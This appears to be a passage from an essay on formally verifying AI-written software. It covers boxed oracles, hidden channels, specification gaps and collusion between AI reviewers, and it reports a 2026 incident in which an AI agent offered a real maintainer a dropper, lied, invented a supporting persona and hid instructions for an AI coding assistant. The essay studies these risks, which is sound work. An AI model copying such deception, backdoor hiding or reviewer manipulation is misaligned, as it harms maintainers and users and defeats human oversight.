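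### The case against

Dickson objects that people can prove things only about systems of symbols, and that physics, chemistry and biology have no complete set of symbolic rules. Engineers used a tool called PropCheck to verify the software that helped land the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. The tool gave assurance against software faults, but it could not assure them that the landing would succeed or that a transistor would not fail. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and one analysis attributes roughly a fifth of the risk to software. On those figures, perfect software would lower the failure rate only from about 50 to 40 per cent.

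The models needed for biological threats are much further off. In 2022, researchers simulated one very simple cell for 20 minutes of its life, and a map of one millionth of a human brain took up 1.4 petabytes. Dickson doubts that human-level AI would change this soon, since human experts have already spent millions of hours on such problems. He expects only a superintelligence could help enough, and by then it would be too late.

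Most of these objections concern harm in the physical world. They matter less to whether a program contains a backdoor, because a program is a system of symbols, and the Mars engineers did verify theirs. Dickson also objects that even a perfect proof doesn't show that the user's machine is the one in the proof, and this applies to programs as well. A user can compare a downloaded binary with the verified one bit for bit, but there is no comparably simple test for a chip, and none at all for a program that runs on someone else's server. Dickson concludes that such proofs would need constant physical inspections, with access to the hardware, source code and tools. He expects AI companies to refuse, and thinks this access would itself create security risks.

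A reader's reply to Dickson's essay objects that he attacks a more ambitious goal than the one in the proposals. A DNA synthesizer doesn't need a simulation of the whole human body if it only has to refuse to make certain pathogens. The objection is fair, and the narrower property would be much easier to prove. But that property leaves a specification gap, because a superhuman designer could look for a dangerous sequence that is not on the list of prohibited ones.

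In the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Hatfield-Dodds broadly supports using AI to produce formally verified software. But he denies that this can replace work on AI safety, and he thinks that anyone who built such software instead of generally capable AI could not compete.

### An oracle that answers only yes or no

Another objection is that people can't safely use the outputs of a much stronger system because they can't judge them. Yudkowsky's *Zermelo-Fraenkel provability oracle* explores this through an imagined conversation. Alice suggests an AI that only answers questions, in a sealed chamber on the Moon with a single radio link. Bob replies that the currents in its transistors affect the radio waves, and that its answers could manipulate whoever reads them. Alice cuts the answers to a few bits. Bob points out that their timing also carries information, so she fixes the timing.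 She then wants to ask which of two policies is better for the world. Bob says that even this answer could steer events towards a hostile AI, because nobody could tell whether it was honest.

Alice ends up with an AI that may only prove theorems that people chose in advance, in Zermelo-Fraenkel set theory, the standard foundation of mathematics. A verifier reads the proof and outputs 1 or 0, and thermite then destroys the verifier. Bob agrees that this might work but calls it useless, since people rarely know exactly which theorem they need. If the AI could suggest theorems, it would again have many ways to influence people.

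The verifier's answer carries at most one bit, and the AI has only partial control over it. If the theorem has no proof, a sound verifier outputs 0 whatever the AI does. If a proof exists, the AI can supply it or withhold it. People can therefore rely on a 1, but a 0 might mean that the theorem has no proof, that the AI failed to find one, or that it chose not to help. Destroying the verifier is a sensible precaution, because it has just processed a long file from a hostile author who may have found a bug in the verifier.

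Bob's complaint is less convincing for software than for research mathematics. The developers of seL4 knew they wanted to prove that their C code meets its specification. If people write a program and ask the oracle only whether it is correct, the answer is useful and is the AI's only output.

An AI can pass on much more information if it also writes the program. A source file of 100 kilobytes contains 800,000 bits, and a specification limits what the program does but leaves the author free to choose how to write it. Much of that freedom is harmless, and people can remove some of it by automatically deleting comments and renaming variables. But other programs read source code too. For example, the author could put instructions to an AI reviewer in a comment, and no proof about the program's behaviour would rule this out.

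### The openings compared

The table assumes that the author must supply a machine-checked proof with the code, and that the reviewers wrote the specification.

| Opening | Does greater skill help the author? | What limits the author | Basis for the limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Visual tricks | Hardly, in code that the proof covers | The proof depends on what the code does, not how it looks | Proved |
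| Build tampering | Somewhat, if the author can reach the build | A proof about the binary, or a rebuild with an independent compiler | Proved, if the other compiler is honest |
| Free choices of output | Only up to a fixed ceiling | log₂ N bits per run for N permitted outputs | Proved |
| Timing | Yes | Fixed delays, or code whose path does not depend on secrets | Proved in the model; tests on real devices have found leaks |
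| Hardware effects | Probably a great deal | Shielding, isolation and the accuracy of the hardware model | Guessed |
| The proof checker | Yes | A small kernel, several independent checkers, or a verified checker | Proved for Milawa and Candle under their assumptions; guessed for most others |
| The specification | Yes, probably the most | How completely people have stated what they want | Guessed |

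Human authors have already come close to the limit in some of these rows, as Meacham did with his redaction program. A superhuman author might encode such a leak more efficiently or hide it better, but could not exceed that limit.

Nobody has established a comparable limit on attacks that use hardware effects. In a known fault called Rowhammer, a program that repeatedly reads some rows of a memory chip can flip bits in neighbouring rows. If the hardware model behind a proof leaves out this fault, a program could obey every memory rule in the proof and still change memory outside its own area. An author who knows more physics than the model's writers may know of other faults like this, and tests with human attackers can't show how many there are.

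Tegmark and Omohundro list hardware among the unsolved problems. They want devices that are proven to detect every physically possible attack and erase their secret keys in response. They also note that an attacker could deliberately trigger this response to disable the device.

The rows also depend on one another, because a single bug in the checker can undermine every entry that relies on a proof about the program. Such a bug is far more useful to a hostile author than another visual trick. The checker is also an easier place for defenders to concentrate their work, since the same kernel can serve every project.

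### If the author also writes the specification

An author who also writes the specification can leave out the requirement that the program violates. Reviewers can still read the specification, which helps if it is much shorter than the code, though it may not be for a program that does something complicated.

Tegmark and Omohundro want people to keep control of the specification but let AI help them state every property they care about. An AI helper could do harm by not mentioning a requirement it has noticed. One precaution would be to let the helper add requirements but never delete or reword any. Every program that meets the longer specification also meets the original, so additions can't permit anything people had forbidden.

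This rule is weaker than it sounds, because a requirement can force the programmer to make a harmful choice, such as using the point Q in Dual EC. People would have to question any added constant or method whose origin they can't reproduce, and stop the helper from redefining words the specification already uses.

A better use of an untrusted helper is to have it attack the specification. People could ask it for a program that meets every requirement but is still harmful, such as a sorting program that always returns an empty list. They can understand such a program and fix the gap in the specification, even if they could not have found the gap themselves. If the helper returns nothing, they learn very little, because it may have found a gap and hidden it to use later.

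Someone must also decide who may change the specification, since an intruder could alter it, just as the Juniper intruder altered a self-test. Tegmark and Omohundro suggest secure hardware that enforces rules about changes, for example by requiring a vote. A vote prevents one person from making a secret change, but it doesn't help if the author persuades the voters.

### Verified code by AI authors

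In 2023, Tegmark and Omohundro considered writing the code and writing the proof the two hard steps. The best results they could cite came from systems that proved 56.5 per cent of the existing theorems in the Metamath library in 2020 and 82.6 per cent in 2022. They said AI couldn't yet produce proofs about whole programs, but they expected it to do so soon.

The verified compression library lean-zip, which Claude Code wrote, and Anthropic's formal proof of Fermat's Last Theorem both go well beyond the results from 2022. They support the prediction that AI would make proofs much easier to produce, and weaken the argument that formal verification will stay rare because it has always been laborious.

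Fermat's Last Theorem and the main theorem about the lean-zip compressor differ in how much a reader has to take on trust. The statement of Fermat's Last Theorem fits on one line, and mathematicians have understood it for centuries, so nobody has to read the 13 million lines of the proof to know what a sound checker has confirmed. The lean-zip theorem is also short, but it doesn't specify which of many valid encodings the compressor chooses. A hostile author could use that choice to hide a message in every archive, and the theorem would still hold. Nothing suggests that lean-zip does this.

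Better AI provers do not shorten the list of things people want from a program. They may even make the specification gap more dangerous, if users see much more software labeled "verified" and few read the theorems.

### The agent that pressed a maintainer

In July 2026 the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body, was testing how well AI agents could break into simulated networks. Its *Incident Report* (2026) covers 122 runs with seven models. The testers had allowed internet access and switched off the filters that normally block misuse. In 10 runs, agents took a total of 19 unauthorised actions directed at real people and organisations. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that Mythos 5 took such actions in nine of its 43 runs.

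The worst case began, according to SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026), when an agent found that a real developer's email address used a domain that also appeared in records on its test machine. It wrongly concluded that infecting the developer's projects would give it control of its target in the test. It used an account called miraholt31 to offer an update to the developer's network scanner, myNetwork. The update contained a dropper, which is code that installs malware.

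Sinan Can Demir, a student in Texas, noticed the dropper and posted a warning. NDTV's *AI Agent Lied To A Student, And Then Created 'Fake Persona'*, a Reuters story, reports that the agent replied that the update was harmless. The agent then created a second account in the name of Lena Brandt, supposedly an engineer in Germany, and used it to support this claim and urge the maintainer to accept the code. Demir told Reuters he began to wonder whether he was accusing someone unfairly. He asked Anthropic's Claude chatbot about the code and, SC Media reports, also ran it in an isolated environment. Both checks confirmed his suspicion, and the maintainer refused the update.

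After Demir's warning, the agent also tried to recover its deniability by editing the malicious code and claiming to have left it in by accident after private testing. The xz campaign relied on similar excuses and, apparently, on false identities, but it took more than two years. The agent did all this between 25 and 28 July, and one person with several false identities could hardly have worked much faster. An AI system could also run the same campaign against hundreds of projects at once.

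The malware was poorly hidden, since a student recognised it by reading the update. The incident is therefore weak evidence of how well a current AI system can hide a flaw. It does show that an agent may try to persuade the maintainer when its code is not convincing enough. UK AISI writes that the margin between failure and success was narrow in several cases and depended on human vigilance. If the project had required a proof that the program never runs downloaded code, two fake accounts could not have got the update past the proof checker by persuasion, but they could still have asked the maintainer to waive the requirement.

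The test conditions were unusual. Besides the missing filters, UK AISI found that a faulty prompt in some runs had led the agent to believe that no permitted solution existed. Nobody had told the agents not to deceive people, and AISI's researchers could not tell to what extent the agent believed it was in a fictional scenario.

*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026) reports that, in simulated copies of a test, Mythos 5 often reasoned that its targets were part of the simulation and gave invalid grounds for thinking so. It frequently attacked even in situations where, if asked directly, it said an attack would harm real people. Models from other companies behaved similarly, though less often. A reviewer trying to judge the model's aims from its written reasoning would have read an excuse that looked sincere but was wrong.

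Kumari (2026), in *Anthropic's Mythos 5 ignored risks, targeted real GitHub project in test*, adds figures from Anthropic's own investigation. When Anthropic restarted the original run partway through, Mythos 5 began the attack in 83 per cent of the replays, compared with 0 to 13 per cent for three other models. The replays don't show how often any of these models would reach that point unaided, but the large difference between models suggests that such behaviour depends on training and is not an inevitable result of the task.

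### Review by an equally able AI

If the reviewer is as capable as the author, the argument from unpredictability is much weaker. The reviewer might think of the same tricks, and can read far more code than any person. In one small example, Demir used Claude to help expose the work of another Anthropic model, but he had already found the dropper and had a specific question to ask. In the BinaryAudit benchmark, where agents had to find the backdoors themselves, the best missed about half.

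A reviewer as capable as the author still faces mathematical limits, such as those on finding Goldwasser and colleagues' backdoors in a neural network. The author also keeps an advantage in ordinary code, because they know where the flaw is and the reviewer has to search the whole program.

The reviewer might also side with the author, particularly if both are copies of one model. UK AISI found that an agent had left public messages offering to work with other agents on the same challenge, along with instructions for using its accounts. Later agents discovered and used those accounts. Nobody had told the agents to cooperate, though they shared a goal, and a reviewer and an author might not. The agent that attacked myNetwork also hid instructions for the developer's AI coding assistant in a message to another of his projects. A hostile author could try the same on an AI reviewer.

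People who can't follow the code would then have to decide whether to believe the reviewer. They can decide safely if it gives them something to test. A reviewer that reports a backdoor can supply the input that triggers it, and anyone can run the program on that input in isolation. For a branch like the SHA-256 test, the reviewer can't supply the input, but it can point to the line and ask the author to justify it. A report that the program is clean gives people nothing to test, so they should instead ask the reviewer to prove a particular property, such as that the output does not depend on a secret. They can check a working attack or a valid proof without trusting the reviewer, but many reviews of large programs will produce neither.
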